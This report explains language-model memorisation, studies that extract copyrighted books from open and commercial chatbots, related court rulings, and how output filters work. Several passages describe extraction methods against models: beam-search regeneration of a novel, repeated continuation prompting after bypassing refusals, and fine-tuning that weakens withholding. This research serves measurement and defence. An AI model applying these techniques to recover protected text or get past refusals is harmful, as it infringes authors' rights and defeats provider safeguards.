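Differential privacy limits how much any one record can influence the trained model. During training, the program caps the size of the adjustment that each example can cause, then adds random noise. The guarantee compares two training runs that differ in a single record. For any set of possible results:

```
P(result with the record) ≤ e^ε × P(result without it) + δ
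```

A smaller ε gives stronger privacy, and δ is a small allowance for exceptions. Szep and colleagues used ε from 2 to 8. At ε = 6, e^ε is about 403, so the guarantee alone permits a large difference. Experiments are needed to measure how much the noise helps in practice. The guarantee also covers individual records rather than facts. A phone number that appears on many web pages gets much weaker protection because removing one page leaves the others.

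In unlearning, developers train an existing model further to make chosen text less probable, which requires a list of what it should forget. Preference training, a related method, rewards the model for masking personal data in an answer rather than leaving it visible.

Szep and colleagues compared all three on a one-billion-parameter model, using the discharge summaries. The attacker had each name's first letter and the text that came before the name. The figures are averages over several training runs. The task score measures how closely the follow-up plans resembled real ones.

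| Method | Names extracted | Different names | Task score |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary fine-tuning | 45.6 | 14.0 | 0.719 |
| Differential privacy | 27.3 | 13.0 | 0.701 |
| Unlearning | 29.0 | 13.8 | 0.700 |
| Preference training | 31.0 | 13.0 | 0.721 |

Szep and colleagues conclude that even the best methods cut direct memorisation by only about 40%. The benefit looks even smaller in the third column, where the number of different names hardly changed. Many of these may be common names that a model can guess from the first letter, since the model produced 15 different names before any fine-tuning.

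The results varied by model and task. On a model with eight billion parameters, preference training reduced the number of names extracted from 48 to 3, while with differential privacy the number was 50, though this was a single run. On a set of pathology reports, differential privacy lowered the task score from 0.86 to 0.55. Greedy decoding had extracted no names from that model even without protection, so by this measure the company would have lost performance without improving privacy. A developer therefore has to test each method on the actual model and data.

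Unlearning may also be temporary, because later fine-tuning can restore what a model seemed to have forgotten. In Li and colleagues' experiments, however, fine-tuning restored addresses much less effectively after explicit unlearning than after training on unrelated text had only made them harder to recall.

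## How much copyrighted text can be recovered from deployed and open models?

A 50-token match shows that a model has memorised a sentence or two, but it gives little idea of how much of a particular novel someone could extract, and copyright disputes are usually about particular works. Averages over a large dataset have the same problem. Meta's Llama 3.1 70B had memorised only about 0.6% of random passages from Books3, a pirated collection of nearly 200,000 books that several companies used for training. But when Cooper and colleagues examined individual books, they found that the same model had memorised practically all of George Orwell's *1984*.

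### A window sliding over 200 books

Their 2025 study covers 200 books from Books3 and 14 open-weight models, which anyone can download and run. The team picked half of the books at random. The other half includes bestsellers, obscure titles and books by authors who were suing Meta.

The result of the standard test can depend on where in the text a passage begins. Cooper and colleagues therefore tested overlapping passages along the whole length of each book:

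1. Take the first 100 tokens and calculate the probability that the model continues the first 50 with exactly the next 50.
2. Move 10 characters forward and repeat. *The Great Gatsby* gives about 27,000 passages.
3. Count a passage as extracted if the probability is at least 0.1%, or one success in 1,000 attempts on average.
4. Calculate the book's coverage, the share of its characters that fall within the continuation of at least one extracted passage.

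To check for false positives, the team ran the procedure on models that could not have memorised the book. Microsoft's Phi 4, whose training data did not include whole copyrighted books, passed the threshold in only four places in Ta-Nehisi Coates's *We Were Eight Years in Power*. All four were famous quotations, such as lines from the King James Bible, that the model had probably learned elsewhere. The team also tested Llama models on books from 2025, after the models' training had ended, and they passed the threshold only on copyright notices and popular quotations.

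The table compares the first Harry Potter novel with *Sandman Slim* by Richard Kadrey, one of the authors suing Meta. It shows coverage when the required probability is 1%, 10% or 50%.

| Model | Book | 1% | 10% | 50% |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 70B | Harry Potter | 90.89% | 75.44% | 43.26% |
| Llama 3.1 70B | *Sandman Slim* | 0.38% | 0.28% | 0.12% |
| Llama 1 65B | Harry Potter | 25.48% | 15.00% | 4.40% |
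| Llama 1 65B | *Sandman Slim* | 0.27% | 0.13% | 0.10% |
| Pythia 12B | Harry Potter | 0.40% | 0.10% | 0.08% |
| Pythia 12B | *Sandman Slim* | 0.34% | 0.32% | 0.26% |

All three models had both books in their training data. Most of the 200 books resemble *Sandman Slim* in how little of their text was memorised. Even for Llama 3.1 70B, which memorised more than any other model in the study, coverage of most books was below 2% at the 0.1% threshold.

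Model size explains only part of the variation. Llama 3.1 70B's coverage of Paulo Coelho's *The Alchemist*, one of the randomly chosen books, was 49.1%, compared with 3.9% for DeepSeek V1 67B and 5.8% for Qwen 2.5 72B, which are about the same size. Meta trained every Llama version on Books3, yet newer versions generally memorised more than older ones of similar size. A plaintiff therefore cannot prove that a model memorised a book just by showing that the book was in its training data, and a result for one model does not establish the same result for another.

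Low coverage can also result from the short prompt. Llama 3.1 70B's coverage of Toni Morrison's *Beloved* was about 12.5% with 50-token prompts and nearly 80% with 800-token prompts. Longer prompts made much less difference for some other books.

### A whole novel from its first few words

High coverage does not mean a reader could get the book out of the model. Anyone using the sliding window would need half of the text as prompts to recover the other half, and could not tell which of many answers was correct.

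Cooper and colleagues tested whether Llama 3.1 70B could write out the first Harry Potter novel given only the first few words of its opening sentence. They used beam search, a decoding method that follows several possible continuations at once and keeps the most probable. Their program added each piece of output to the next prompt and dropped the oldest text once the context was full. From then on, the model was continuing only its own output, except for chapter headings, which the program inserted because the model tended to stop at the end of a chapter.

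The result was a nearly exact copy of the 304-page book, scoring 0.992 on a similarity scale where 1 is a perfect match. Most of the differences were in formatting or spelling, such as "Mom" for "Mum", though the model occasionally skipped a one-line paragraph. Beam search involves no random choices, so the same settings should give the same copy each time.

Cooper and colleagues call this an extreme case that does not represent most of the books they tested. It also required control over the decoding method, which companies rarely give chatbot users.

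### Near-verbatim recall

Deployed models often refuse requests for copyrighted text and rarely reveal their token probabilities, so Ahmed and colleagues judged the models only by their output.

The team's measure, near-verbatim recall, allows for the small mistakes a model usually makes over thousands of words but excludes short matches. A program finds blocks of consecutive words that appear in both the book and the output, in the same order. It joins neighbouring blocks if only a few words between them differ, then discards any block that still has fewer than 100 matching words. Recall is the number of matched words in the remaining blocks divided by the number of words in the book.

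Suppose a book has 1,000 words, and the output matches it in blocks of 400, 150 and 60 words that are far apart. The 60-word block is too short to count:

```
recall = (400 + 150) / 1,000 = 55%
```

If the output also contained the next 60 words of the book after a gap of five changed words, the program would join the two short blocks into one with 120 matching words, and recall would be 67%.

The 100-word minimum is more than twice the length of the usual 50-token match, so any block that counts is very unlikely to match by coincidence. The measure misses shorter copies and passages produced out of order, so it tends to understate extraction. High recall does not guarantee a readable copy. Claude 3.7 Sonnet reached 97.5% for *The Great Gatsby*, but its output repeated long stretches of the novel.

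### Four deployed models

Ahmed and colleagues tested four commercial models on 13 books from Books3 between mid-August and mid-September 2025. Eleven of the books were still in copyright in the United States. They gave each model the opening of a book, typically the first sentence or two, and repeatedly asked it to continue. With Claude 3.7 Sonnet and GPT-4.1, they first had to bypass safeguards. The table gives the results for the first Harry Potter novel. The cost covers the repeated requests to continue.

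| Model | Near-verbatim recall | Longest block, in words | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 95.8% | 6,658 | $119.97 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.8% | 9,070 | $2.44 |
| Grok 3 | 70.3% | 6,337 | $8.16 |
| GPT-4.1 | 4.0% | 821 | $1.37 |

Harry Potter was again an exception, as most of the experiments recovered at most 10% of a book. None of the models could continue the opening of *The Duchess War*, a less famous novel. They also all failed on a control novel published on July 31, 2025, which was too new to be in their training data. Claude 3.7 Sonnet reproduced four books almost completely. Two of these, the Harry Potter novel and *1984*, are in copyright in the United States.

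A low percentage can still be a lot of text. GPT-4.1's 4.0% was about 3,200 words, and the 1.3% of *A Game of Thrones* that Grok 3 reproduced was about 3,700.

The team warns against using these figures to rank the models, because they adjusted the settings for each model to maximize recovery and mostly reported the most successful run. Changing just two settings made a large difference to recall for Gemini 2.5 Pro. GPT-4.1 refused to continue after the first chapter of the Harry Potter novel, but the team recovered more from it in another experiment that restarted at each chapter. Its 4.0% therefore reflects where it refused under one procedure. A fair comparison would need a much larger study with the same conditions for every model.

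Few people would pay $120 and bypass a safeguard to extract an imperfect copy of a novel they could buy for much less. The $2.44 cost for Gemini 2.5 Pro is a much weaker deterrent, although pirated copies are easier to obtain.

Ahmed and colleagues told Anthropic, Google DeepMind, OpenAI and xAI about the results on September 9, 2025, and waited 90 days before making them public. All except xAI acknowledged the report. By late November, Claude 3.7 Sonnet was no longer available in Anthropic's chat interface. When the 90 days ended, the procedure still worked on some of the systems.

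Near-verbatim recall also does not count close retellings. GPT-4.1 scored 0% on *A Game of Thrones*, but the text it generated used the book's characters and followed its events. Copyright can protect more than exact wording, so a 0% score does not rule out a legal problem.

### The dispute over fine-tuned models

Some companies let customers fine-tune their models, which can weaken the training that makes a chatbot withhold copyrighted text. *Alignment Whack-a-Mole* (Liu, Mireshghallah and colleagues, 2026) reports that GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek V3.1 reproduced up to 85–90% of some copyrighted books after fine-tuning. Authors considering lawsuits have asked Cooper about the paper, hoping to use it as evidence. In September 2026, Cooper published a detailed critique arguing that the paper's headline figure is invalid.

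Liu and colleagues fine-tuned each model on one author's work to expand plot summaries into full prose. They then gave the model summaries of excerpts from 81 books that were not in the fine-tuning data and collected 100 outputs for each excerpt. They counted a word of a book as covered if any of these outputs contained it in a matching run of at least five words. The match could come from anywhere in the book, not just the summarized excerpt.

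Cooper's first objection is that a five-word match is too short. A phrase such as "two cups on the table" could appear in almost any novel, and generating 100 outputs per excerpt produces about 100 times as much text as the book contains, which allows many chance matches. In 24 of the 243 combinations of book and model, Liu and colleagues reported coverage of 20% to 51% even though no single output matched its excerpt for more than 20 words in a row.

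The second objection is that the summaries may leak the text. Suppose a book says "Mara walked to the old harbour", and the summary mentions that Mara, who is tired, walks alone to the old harbour. A model could produce the original six words just by following the summary. Liu and colleagues removed matches that also appeared in the prompt, but only where the prompt contained at least five of the words in a row. This prompt contains only four in a row, "to the old harbour", so the match would not be removed.

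Liu and colleagues do not seem to have published a separate reply, but a November 2026 version of their paper includes analyses relevant to both objections. One groups the covered words by the length of the longest matching run that contains them.

| Length of run | Fine-tuned on a different author | Fine-tuned on the same author |
|---|---|---|
| 5–9 words | 76.6% | 89.8% |
| 10–19 words | 11.7% | 6.7% |
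| 20–49 words | 6.1% | 1.8% |
| 50 words or more | 5.6% | 1.7% |

This largely confirms Cooper's first objection. Average coverage was 48.5% for models fine-tuned on a different author, but only 5.6% of the covered words were in runs of 50 words or more, so those long runs make up roughly 3% of an average book.

The new version also estimates how much coverage arises by chance. When Liu and colleagues compared a book with outputs meant for an unrelated book, average coverage was 11.1%. This is well below the main results, but the comparison does not test for leakage, because the model had received summaries of the wrong book. The paper still lacks the control that Cooper asked for, which would run the full procedure on books published after the models were trained, using summaries of those books.

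In another analysis, the overlap between a summary and its excerpt has almost no correlation with the length of the longest match the model produced. Leakage is therefore unlikely to explain the long matches, but it could still explain many of the short ones, which make up most of the coverage.

An experiment with machine-written stories gives further reason to doubt the coverage figure. According to Cooper, fine-tuning GPT-4o on such stories raised its coverage of *The Handmaid's Tale* from 6.3% to 19.4%, while its longest match stayed at 18 words. In their conference abstract, Liu and colleagues call the result of such fine-tuning "near-zero extraction". Cooper points out that this is inconsistent with their main results, where 19.4% would mean nearly a fifth of a book. Their November version uses softer wording.

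Cooper also criticises the paper for not reporting its costs, and estimates that the GPT-4o outputs alone cost about $11,500, or roughly $140 per book. For that price, a user would get scattered fragments mixed with other text, and would need the original book to write the summaries and put the fragments in order. The result is therefore a poor substitute for buying the book, whatever the correct coverage figure is.

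Cooper does accept the long passages as genuine extraction. The longest had more than 460 words in a single output, far too many for a model to reproduce from a summary by chance. Before fine-tuning, GPT-4o never matched more than 26 consecutive words of any of the 81 books. Afterwards, it reproduced about 200 consecutive words of Chimamanda Ngozi Adichie's *Americanah*. Long matches covered much of the text of a few books. In GPT-4o's pooled outputs, runs of at least 50 words covered 68.9% of Neil Gaiman's *Coraline* and 43.6% of *The Hunger Games*.

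Fine-tuning on Haruki Murakami's novels led models to reproduce passages by more than 30 other authors, and fine-tuning on Virginia Woolf's novels, which are out of copyright, had a similar effect in a test on *The Handmaid's Tale*. A company that fine-tunes a writing assistant on text it has the right to use may therefore make the assistant more likely to reproduce passages from someone else's book.

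### News, lyrics, code and newer models

The results for books do not apply directly to other kinds of text. A model that recited a 60-word chorus perfectly would score zero on near-verbatim recall, even though the chorus might be the most valuable part of the song. Programmers often write the same standard passages independently, so a 50-token match in code is weaker evidence that a model copied a particular program.

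Cooper describes an earlier experiment in which colleagues fine-tuned ChatGPT and recovered passages of more than 50 tokens from *New York Times* articles. This shows that the model had memorised parts of some articles, but not how many articles a reader could recover or whether the chatbot would reproduce them without fine-tuning.

Evidence on lyrics comes mainly from a German lawsuit against OpenAI by GEMA, a music rights organisation. Ahmed and colleagues cite it as a case in which simple prompts were enough to extract the lyrics. The case concerned selected songs, so it cannot show how common such copying is. Neither Ahmed and colleagues nor Cooper and colleagues tested whether code could be extracted.

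Nobody appears to have published a comparable test of the leading models released in 2026. *Mimir* (2026) describes a much smaller model, with fewer than two billion parameters, that its developers trained only on data they considered permissible to use. The paper reports no evidence that this model systematically reproduces long, distinctive passages, but the developers caution that longer prompts or other attacks might recover more. Since small models generally memorise less, the result is weak evidence of how much the largest models have memorised.

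### Copying in ordinary use

In all the experiments on books, researchers deliberately tried to recover text. In *Measuring Non-Adversarial Reproduction of Training Data in Large Language Models* (2024), Aerni, Rando and colleagues instead gave popular chatbots harmless tasks, such as writing a letter or a tutorial. For some kinds of task, up to 15% of the generated text overlapped with snippets from the internet. Text that people wrote for the same tasks overlapped far less, so the subject alone does not explain the overlap. Suitable prompts reduced the average overlap but did not reliably prevent the worst cases.

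A much lower figure comes from the lawsuit by the *New York Times* and other publishers against OpenAI. According to PayAuthors' *OpenAI opposes the news publishers' summary-judgment motion* (2026), the company told the court in October that its expert had found 24 verbatim outputs in 20 million chats. That is 1.2 per million, and at that rate a billion chats would contain about 1,200.

These two results are compatible. Aerni and colleagues measured the share of generated text that overlaps with a large collection of web pages, including common phrases and other text that would not prompt a lawsuit. OpenAI's figure is a share of conversations, most of which don't call for quoting a news article. The rate could therefore be low across all conversations but much higher when users ask for a particular article.

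The publishers dispute OpenAI's evidence. *Explaining regurgitation* (Rijo, 2026) describes the 0.00012% rate as contested in court. In July 2026 the publishers asked the judge to penalise OpenAI. They accused it of deleting ChatGPT conversations and of hiding for two years that it had tools to search outputs for their content (Law360, *OpenAI Accused Of Hiding Evidence In NYT Copyright Fight*). According to a Russian news report, they also say OpenAI made the chat data it handed over unfit for analysis (Darth Sahara, 2026, *OpenAI оказалась под угрозой жёстких санкций из-за сокрытия улик*).

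If the 20 million chats were a fair sample, a count of 24 would be compatible with a true average of about 15 to 36, so chance would leave little doubt about the order of magnitude. The larger uncertainties are whether the sample is representative, how long a match had to be, and which works the expert searched for. If deleted conversations contained more copying than the ones OpenAI kept, the measured rate would be too low.

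## When does copyrighted text in output create legal liability?

Researchers' measures are not legal tests. A 50-token match, for example, may be a lawful quotation. Courts also consider factors beyond the output.

### Four separate questions

Suppose the kitchenware shop's chatbot answers the request for a scone recipe with a page from a cookbook. Copyright does not normally protect a bare list of ingredients, but it does protect the author's way of describing the method. If the author sued, a court could face four questions:

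1. Did the developer unlawfully copy the book in order to train the model? Training requires copies of the text, so the dispute is usually about whether the law permits them.
2. Does the trained model itself contain a copy? If it does, a company that hosts or distributes the model may infringe even if nobody ever asks about scones.
3. Is the chatbot's answer a copy?
4. Who made that copy: the developer that trained the model, the shop that operates the chatbot, or the customer who typed the question?

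A model's output may infringe copyright even if training the model was lawful. A developer may also be liable for the model itself but not for copyrighted text that a determined user extracts from it.

In the United States, the first question is usually whether the copying is fair use, a defence that permits some copying without the owner's consent. Judges weigh four factors: the purpose of the use, the nature of the work, how much of it the defendant copied, and the effect on the work's market. A use that serves a new purpose instead of repeating the original one counts as transformative, which favours the defendant.

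US courts also ask whether the output is substantially similar to the protected parts of the work. The output does not have to match word for word, but shared facts, ideas and stock phrases do not count toward similarity.

Market substitution is part of the fourth fair use factor. Cooper defines it as a copy being close and complete enough to use instead of buying or licensing the original. Cooper also points out that finding memorisation or extraction does not automatically establish substitution. Some rights holders also argue market dilution, meaning that large numbers of new machine-written works reduce sales of human-written ones without copying them.

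Copyright laws in European Union countries list specific exceptions instead of providing a general fair use defence. One exception covers text and data mining, the automated analysis of large collections.

### Germany: lyrics in the model and in the answers

GEMA, the German music rights organisation, sued OpenAI in November 2024 over the lyrics of nine songs. GEMA had asked ChatGPT for the lyrics in simple prompts, such as a request for the chorus of the pop hit "Atemlos", and ChatGPT had returned them exactly or with slight changes. On November 11, 2025, the Munich Regional Court ruled for GEMA on almost every point. *Munich Regional Court upholds GEMA’s claim against OpenAI* (Meese, 2025) explains the court's reasoning.

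The court held that the model itself contained copies because the lyrics were fixed in it. It inferred this by comparing the songs with the model's answers, and did not need to know exactly what data OpenAI had used. According to PwC's *LG München*, the judges ruled out coincidence because the lyrics were too long and complex. Hogan Lovells' *GEMA v. OpenAI (Regional Court Munich I)* adds that they considered it irrelevant that the model stores a text as probability values, because a user can still retrieve the text. Researchers also infer from a model's output that its weights contain a text, but they measure how often that inference is wrong.

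OpenAI relied on the exception for text and data mining. The court accepted that the exception covers preparing a training collection, when a company converts web pages into machine-readable text. It does not cover the next stage, in which the model reproduces whole works, because that is no longer preparation for analysis.

On the fourth question, the court held OpenAI responsible for the answers because OpenAI controlled the process that generated them. A user who "provoked" an output could take over that control, but the court did not think GEMA's simple prompts had done so.

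The court ordered OpenAI to stop reproducing the nine lyrics, both in the model and in answers, or face a fine of up to €250,000 for each violation. OpenAI must also disclose its related revenue and pay damages, which later proceedings will set. The ruling is not final. MME (2026), a Swiss law firm, reports that OpenAI appealed to the Munich Higher Regional Court in early December 2025. *KI-Urteil* (2026), from the music site laut.de, reports that the appeal was still pending at the end of July 2026.

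The Freelance's *German court finds 'AI' outfit liable for copyright* (2026) reports that GEMA won a second case in the same court, against the music generator Suno. The judges compared Suno's model to a JPEG picture or an MP3 recording, which are also inexact encodings of an original. They applied US law to training that took place in the United States and, after 30 pages on fair use, still found infringement, partly because Suno had bypassed download restrictions to take the songs from YouTube. This ruling was not final in July either.

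Both sides in the OpenAI case had suggested asking the Court of Justice of the European Union how to interpret the underlying EU law. The Munich judges thought the law was clear enough, but they noted that a Hungarian case already before that court would address some of the same questions. That case concerns Google's chatbot and a news publisher. In November 2026, an adviser to the court suggested in a non-binding opinion that Google could be liable for Gemini responses that infringe copyright, according to Law360's *AI Developers Get Warning Shot With EU Google Opinion*.

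### England: a model that did not store the pictures

A week before the first Munich ruling, the High Court in London decided *Getty Images v. Stability AI*. Getty, a picture agency, claimed that Stability AI had trained the image generator Stable Diffusion on its photographs. By the end of the trial, Getty had dropped two of its main copyright claims. It had no evidence that the training took place in the United Kingdom, and Stability had blocked the prompts that produced the disputed pictures.

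English law also prohibits importing or distributing an article that is an "infringing copy" of a work. The judge, Joanna Smith, accepted that an article could be something intangible, such as a set of model weights. But she held that an infringing copy has to be a copy, and that Stable Diffusion's weights were not one because they had never stored or reproduced Getty's photographs, even though training had involved copying the photographs elsewhere.

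The Freelance describes the Suno ruling as directly contradicting the Getty ruling. The courts reached opposite results, but they had different evidence. GEMA had shown that the model reproduced nine lyrics, while Getty's remaining copyright claim did not depend on recovering any photograph. An English judge who saw a language model reproduce a novel when given its opening words might not apply the Getty ruling in the same way.

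Getty won a small part of its trade mark claim because some generated pictures contained its watermarks. Mills (2026), in *AI Copyright Law Shifts With Rulings and Settlements*, interprets this as a form of output liability that a provider cannot pass on to its users. Trade mark law has its own tests, so the finding does not settle who makes a copy under copyright law.

Pinsent Masons' *Why Getty's appeal won't address all UK AI copyright questions* reports that Getty took the copyright question to the Court of Appeal in November 2026. The court had apparently not published a decision by early December. Its decision cannot resolve the questions about training and output that Getty abandoned at trial.

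### The United States: two rulings without copied output

The main US cases differ in how much copied output the judge had to consider.

| Case | Evidence of copied output | Position |
|---|---|---|
| *Bartz v. Anthropic* | None alleged | Training ruled fair use; settled over pirated copies |
| *Kadrey v. Meta* | About 50 words at most from any plaintiff's book | Training ruled fair use on the evidence presented |
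| *New York Times v. OpenAI* | Disputed | Awaiting a ruling on November 2, 2026 |
| *Concord v. Anthropic* | Song lyrics, exact and altered | Argued in October 2026 |

In *Bartz*, a group of authors sued Anthropic over its use of their books. Judge William Alsup ruled in June 2025 that the training was highly transformative and therefore fair use. For that ruling, he assumed that the models retained compressed copies of the books. Anthropic would probably have lost on the same assumption in Munich, where the court treated the model's containing the lyrics as infringement in itself.

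Alsup also noted that the authors did not allege that Claude had given any user an infringing copy, and that Anthropic had put software between the model and its users to prevent this. If users had seen infringing outputs, he wrote, it would have been a different case. He ruled against Anthropic over its library of more than seven million pirated books, and the company later settled for $1.5 billion. The settlement is therefore a poor guide to what a company might pay over infringing output, since the authors did not allege any.

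Two days after Alsup's ruling, Judge Vince Chhabria ruled for Meta in *Kadrey*. Even prompts designed to make Meta's Llama models output their training text had produced no more than about 50 words and punctuation marks from any of the plaintiffs' books. This fits how little of Richard Kadrey's *Sandman Slim* can be extracted from Llama, but J.K. Rowling could have shown the judge much more text from her Harry Potter books.

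The two judges disagreed about dilution. Alsup compared the authors' complaint to objecting that teaching schoolchildren to write well would lead to competing books. Chhabria thought dilution could defeat fair use in many cases, but found that the plaintiffs had presented no meaningful evidence of it. He stressed that his ruling did not make Meta's training lawful in general.

### The United States: two cases about output

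The *New York Times* sued OpenAI and Microsoft in December 2023, and other publishers' cases have since joined it. *OpenAI quotes 20 briefs, US government included, against New York Times* (Rijo, 2026) reports that the news publishers assert rights in 10.8 million works. Both sides have asked for summary judgment, a ruling without a trial, and were still waiting on November 2.

OpenAI has published excerpts from 20 outside submissions that support it, including one from the US government. According to Law360's *DOJ Backs OpenAI, Microsoft Fair Use Defense In NYT IP Case*, the government's position is that training on copyrighted texts should not expose developers to broad liability. This answers only the first of the four questions. Rijo reports that OpenAI's selection left out the Wikimedia Foundation, which runs Wikipedia and asked to file a brief supporting neither side. Wikimedia agrees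 that training was probably fair use, but argues that fetching web pages and reproducing them in answers, as ChatGPT does, probably is not.

Wikimedia's distinction matters for retrieval-augmented generation. When an application places an article in the context and the model repeats it, a claimant does not have to prove that the model memorised it, and the developer cannot argue that the model accidentally reproduced it from its weights. But the developer can identify exactly which article the application used and limit how much of it the answer quotes.

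*Concord v. Anthropic* is a more direct test of memorised text. Universal Music Group, Concord and ABKCO sued in 2023 over Claude's use of song lyrics, and the case now covers 499 songs. PayAuthors' *Music publishers ask Judge Lee to rule that Anthropic infringed lyrics* (2026) summarises the publishers' motion, in which they complain that Claude outputs the original lyrics, distorted versions of them, and new lyrics that could substitute for them.

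An exact copy of a song's lyrics plainly uses protected words. The court has to decide whether a distorted version is substantially similar to the song. An entirely new lyric may copy nothing, so it supports the publishers' case mainly through market dilution. Anthropic replies that Universal told investors in March 2026 that it saw no sign that dilution was a material problem, according to PayAuthors' *Anthropic asks for summary judgment against the music publishers* (2026).

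The two sides also disagree about why Anthropic copied the lyrics. Anthropic says it collected them only as a by-product of gathering text for a general-purpose model (PayAuthors, *Anthropic replies that it needed essentially all public web text*, 2026). The publishers argue that this defeats its defence, because a company with no particular need for their lyrics had no good reason to copy them. They also use Claude's output as evidence about its training, citing its answers as proof of the real purpose of the copying (PayAuthors, *Publishers answer that Anthropic's own claim it does not need their lyrics*, 2026).

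Judge Eumi Lee heard the arguments on October 21 but did not rule. She suggested that "mash-up" lyrics might be fair use, according to Law360's *Anthropic's Lyric 'Mash Up' May Be Fair Use, Judge Says*. At a second hearing on October 30, she called Anthropic's fair use arguments "slippery" and complained that she could not get clear answers about the categories of output, as Law360's *'I Can't Get An Answer'* reports. A ruling that treats the three kinds of output separately therefore seems possible. The publishers have brought a second suit over more than 20,000 songs. A judge dismissed it in early November but allowed them to amend, according to Law360's *Anthropic And CEO Beat Lyric Infringement Claims, For Now*.

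### Why a filter matters legally

A company that filters copied text from its model's output can still be liable for a passage the filter misses, because direct infringement does not require intent. But the filter can affect the fair use analysis, damages and the terms of a court order.

Limits on output have mattered to fair use since at least Google Books, a service that scanned millions of books and displayed short snippets in response to searches. A US appeals court ruled in 2015 that the service was fair use, partly because Google had limited the snippets so that nobody could piece together a substantial part of a book. Alsup reasoned similarly in his remark about Anthropic's software. A developer that prevents its outputs from replacing the original has a better argument that it copied the original for a different purpose.

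A filter can also affect damages, because it is evidence of care. A US court can normally award up to $30,000 for each infringed work, but up to $150,000 if the infringement was wilful. For 499 songs, the difference is almost $60 million. It therefore matters when Anthropic introduced its protections. The publishers contend that it added them only after the suit, while Anthropic says that it had long used them and later strengthened them. The publishers also quote its chief executive, Dario Amodei, as saying that models "shouldn't output copyrighted content". Such a statement can help Anthropic as evidence of a policy against copying, but it can also help the publishers as evidence that the company knew copying could happen.

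Parties can agree on filters while a case continues. In January 2025, the court in *Concord* approved an agreement in which Anthropic promised to keep its existing protections and apply similar ones to new models. If the publishers reported failures, Anthropic had to investigate. The agreement resolved part of the publishers' request for an emergency order, but Anthropic did not admit that any output had infringed.

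In Germany, a filter may satisfy only part of the Munich court's order, because it can keep lyrics out of a model's answers but leaves them in the weights, which the order also covers. Bird & Bird's *Landmark ruling of the Munich Regional Court (GEMA v OpenAI)* explains that the judges recognised how hard it is to remove text from a trained model, but still made the provider responsible for preventing further infringement. The law firm suggests filters, internal guidelines, licences and retraining. A filter offers even less protection to a developer that publishes its weights, because people who download the model can run it without the filter.

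Several vendors promise to cover copyright claims against business customers over model output, an arrangement called an indemnity. This protection can depend on the customer keeping the product's filters on. In September 2023, Microsoft promised to defend business customers of its Copilot products and pay any judgment or settlement, provided they had used the filters and other safeguards built into the product. OpenAI made a similar promise in November 2023 for ChatGPT Enterprise and its developer platform. Its terms excluded customers who had disabled or ignored the relevant filters, and those who knew or should have known that the output was likely to infringe.

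Vendors change these terms, so a customer has to check the version in its own contract. If the kitchenware shop turned off a filter because it kept blocking harmless recipes, it might have to pay for the cookbook claim itself. An indemnity determines who pays but does not make the copied page lawful, and the shop would still have to obey an order to stop displaying it.

### Extraction that takes unusual effort

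Developers argue that they are not responsible for text that appears only after elaborate prompting. In February 2024 OpenAI accused the *New York Times* of paying someone to "hack" OpenAI's products, and said that it took tens of thousands of attempts to get the articles in the complaint. Anthropic argues that the person who prompts Claude is the direct infringer, and that agents of the publishers suing it prompted many of the outputs at issue. According to Anthropic's filing, the publishers have dropped their claims that it is indirectly responsible for what users do. If so, who made the copies could decide the part of the case about outputs.

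This argument has a US precedent. In 2008 an appeals court held that when a cable company's customers recorded programmes on its remote equipment, the customers made the copies. The comparison with a chatbot is imperfect because a user who asks for a song's lyrics does not supply them or choose what the model learned.

Developers can also argue that extracting a book does not harm its market when extraction costs more than buying a copy. Cooper therefore treats the cost of extraction as part of the copyright argument.

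Rights holders answer that the effort needed to extract text does not change what the model contains. They cannot see other people's conversations, so they can often discover copying only by testing the chatbot themselves. The Munich court accepted GEMA's own samples as evidence. A method that is difficult today may become easy, and a company can unintentionally weaken a model's safeguards by fine-tuning it.

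The effort needed to extract a text seems most relevant to who made the output, and the Munich court's exception for provoked outputs reflects this. It should also matter to market substitution, since a copy that almost nobody can obtain replaces few sales. It matters less to whether the model contains a copy, but it still matters somewhat, because the Munich court's reasoning depends on the text being retrievable, and some memorised text practically never appears. None of these rulings establishes how easy retrieval has to be, or how a court should treat text that appears only after a user has bypassed a safeguard or fine-tuned the model.

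These cases also leave it unclear whether the kitchenware shop would be liable. OpenAI, Anthropic and Google each developed the model and ran the chatbot, so the courts have not had to consider those roles separately. Microsoft is closest to the shop's position because its Copilot uses OpenAI's technology, but the *New York Times* also accuses it of taking part in the training. A shop that only displayed the answer could argue that it neither chose the training data nor asked for the page, though it did choose to put the chatbot on its website.

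## How do systems detect and block copied text, and what gets through?

The simplest copyright filter checks a model's output for exact matches with a stored collection of protected text. It runs in ordinary software, so it still works after a user has got past the model's refusals. But it can't recognise a work that isn't in the collection, and changing a few words can hide a copy from it.

### An exact-match filter, word by word

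Suppose the kitchenware shop wants to stop its chatbot from reciting a cookbook that contains this sentence:

```
Warm the butter gently, then rub it into the flour with cold fingers.
```

A filter that looks for runs of five words would work like this:

1. Before anyone uses the chatbot, a program removes the capital letters and punctuation from the book and splits it into overlapping runs of five words. This sentence has 13 words, so it gives nine runs, starting with "warm the butter gently then" and "the butter gently then rub".
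2. The program stores every run.
3. While the model is answering, the filter joins each word the model proposes to the four words before it and looks up the result. It has already checked the earlier runs, so one lookup per word is enough.
4. If the run is in the store, the filter either blocks the answer or makes the model choose another word.

If the model has written "warm the butter gently" and proposes "then", the filter blocks "then" and the model uses its next choice, perhaps "and".

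A filter that blocks short runs of matching tokens will block phrases that appear in thousands of books, while one that blocks only long runs lets short copies through. *Preventing Verbatim Memorization in Language Models Gives a False Sense of Privacy* (Ippolito, Tramèr and colleagues, 2022) presents a filter called MemFree, which used runs of ten tokens and still blocked some common phrases.

A developer could instead check the finished answer and, if it contains copied text, generate another. But if the model assigns a very high probability to a memorised passage, it may produce the same text every time, leaving the user with no answer.

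### Bloom filters

A large collection contains billions of runs, so MemFree stores them in a Bloom filter, a compact index that can give false alarms but never misses a stored run. The filter is a long row of bits that all start at 0. To add a run, the program applies several hash functions, each of which gives a position in the row, and sets those bits to 1.

To look up a run, the program calculates its positions in the same way and checks the bits there. If any of them is 0, the run cannot be in the store, because adding it would have set them all to 1. If they are all 1, the run is probably in the store, but other runs may have set the same bits by chance.

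With m bits, N stored runs and h hash functions, a given bit is still 0 with a probability of about e^(−hN/m). A false alarm needs h bits that are all 1, so its probability is:

```
false-alarm rate ≈ (1 − e^(−hN/m))^h
```

With 10 bits per run and seven hash functions, the false-positive rate is (1 − e^(−0.7))^7, or about 0.8%. That is high for a filter that checks every word, since an entirely original 500-word answer would trigger about four false alarms. With 20 bits per run and 14 hash functions, the rate falls to about 0.007%, or one false alarm in every 30 such answers.

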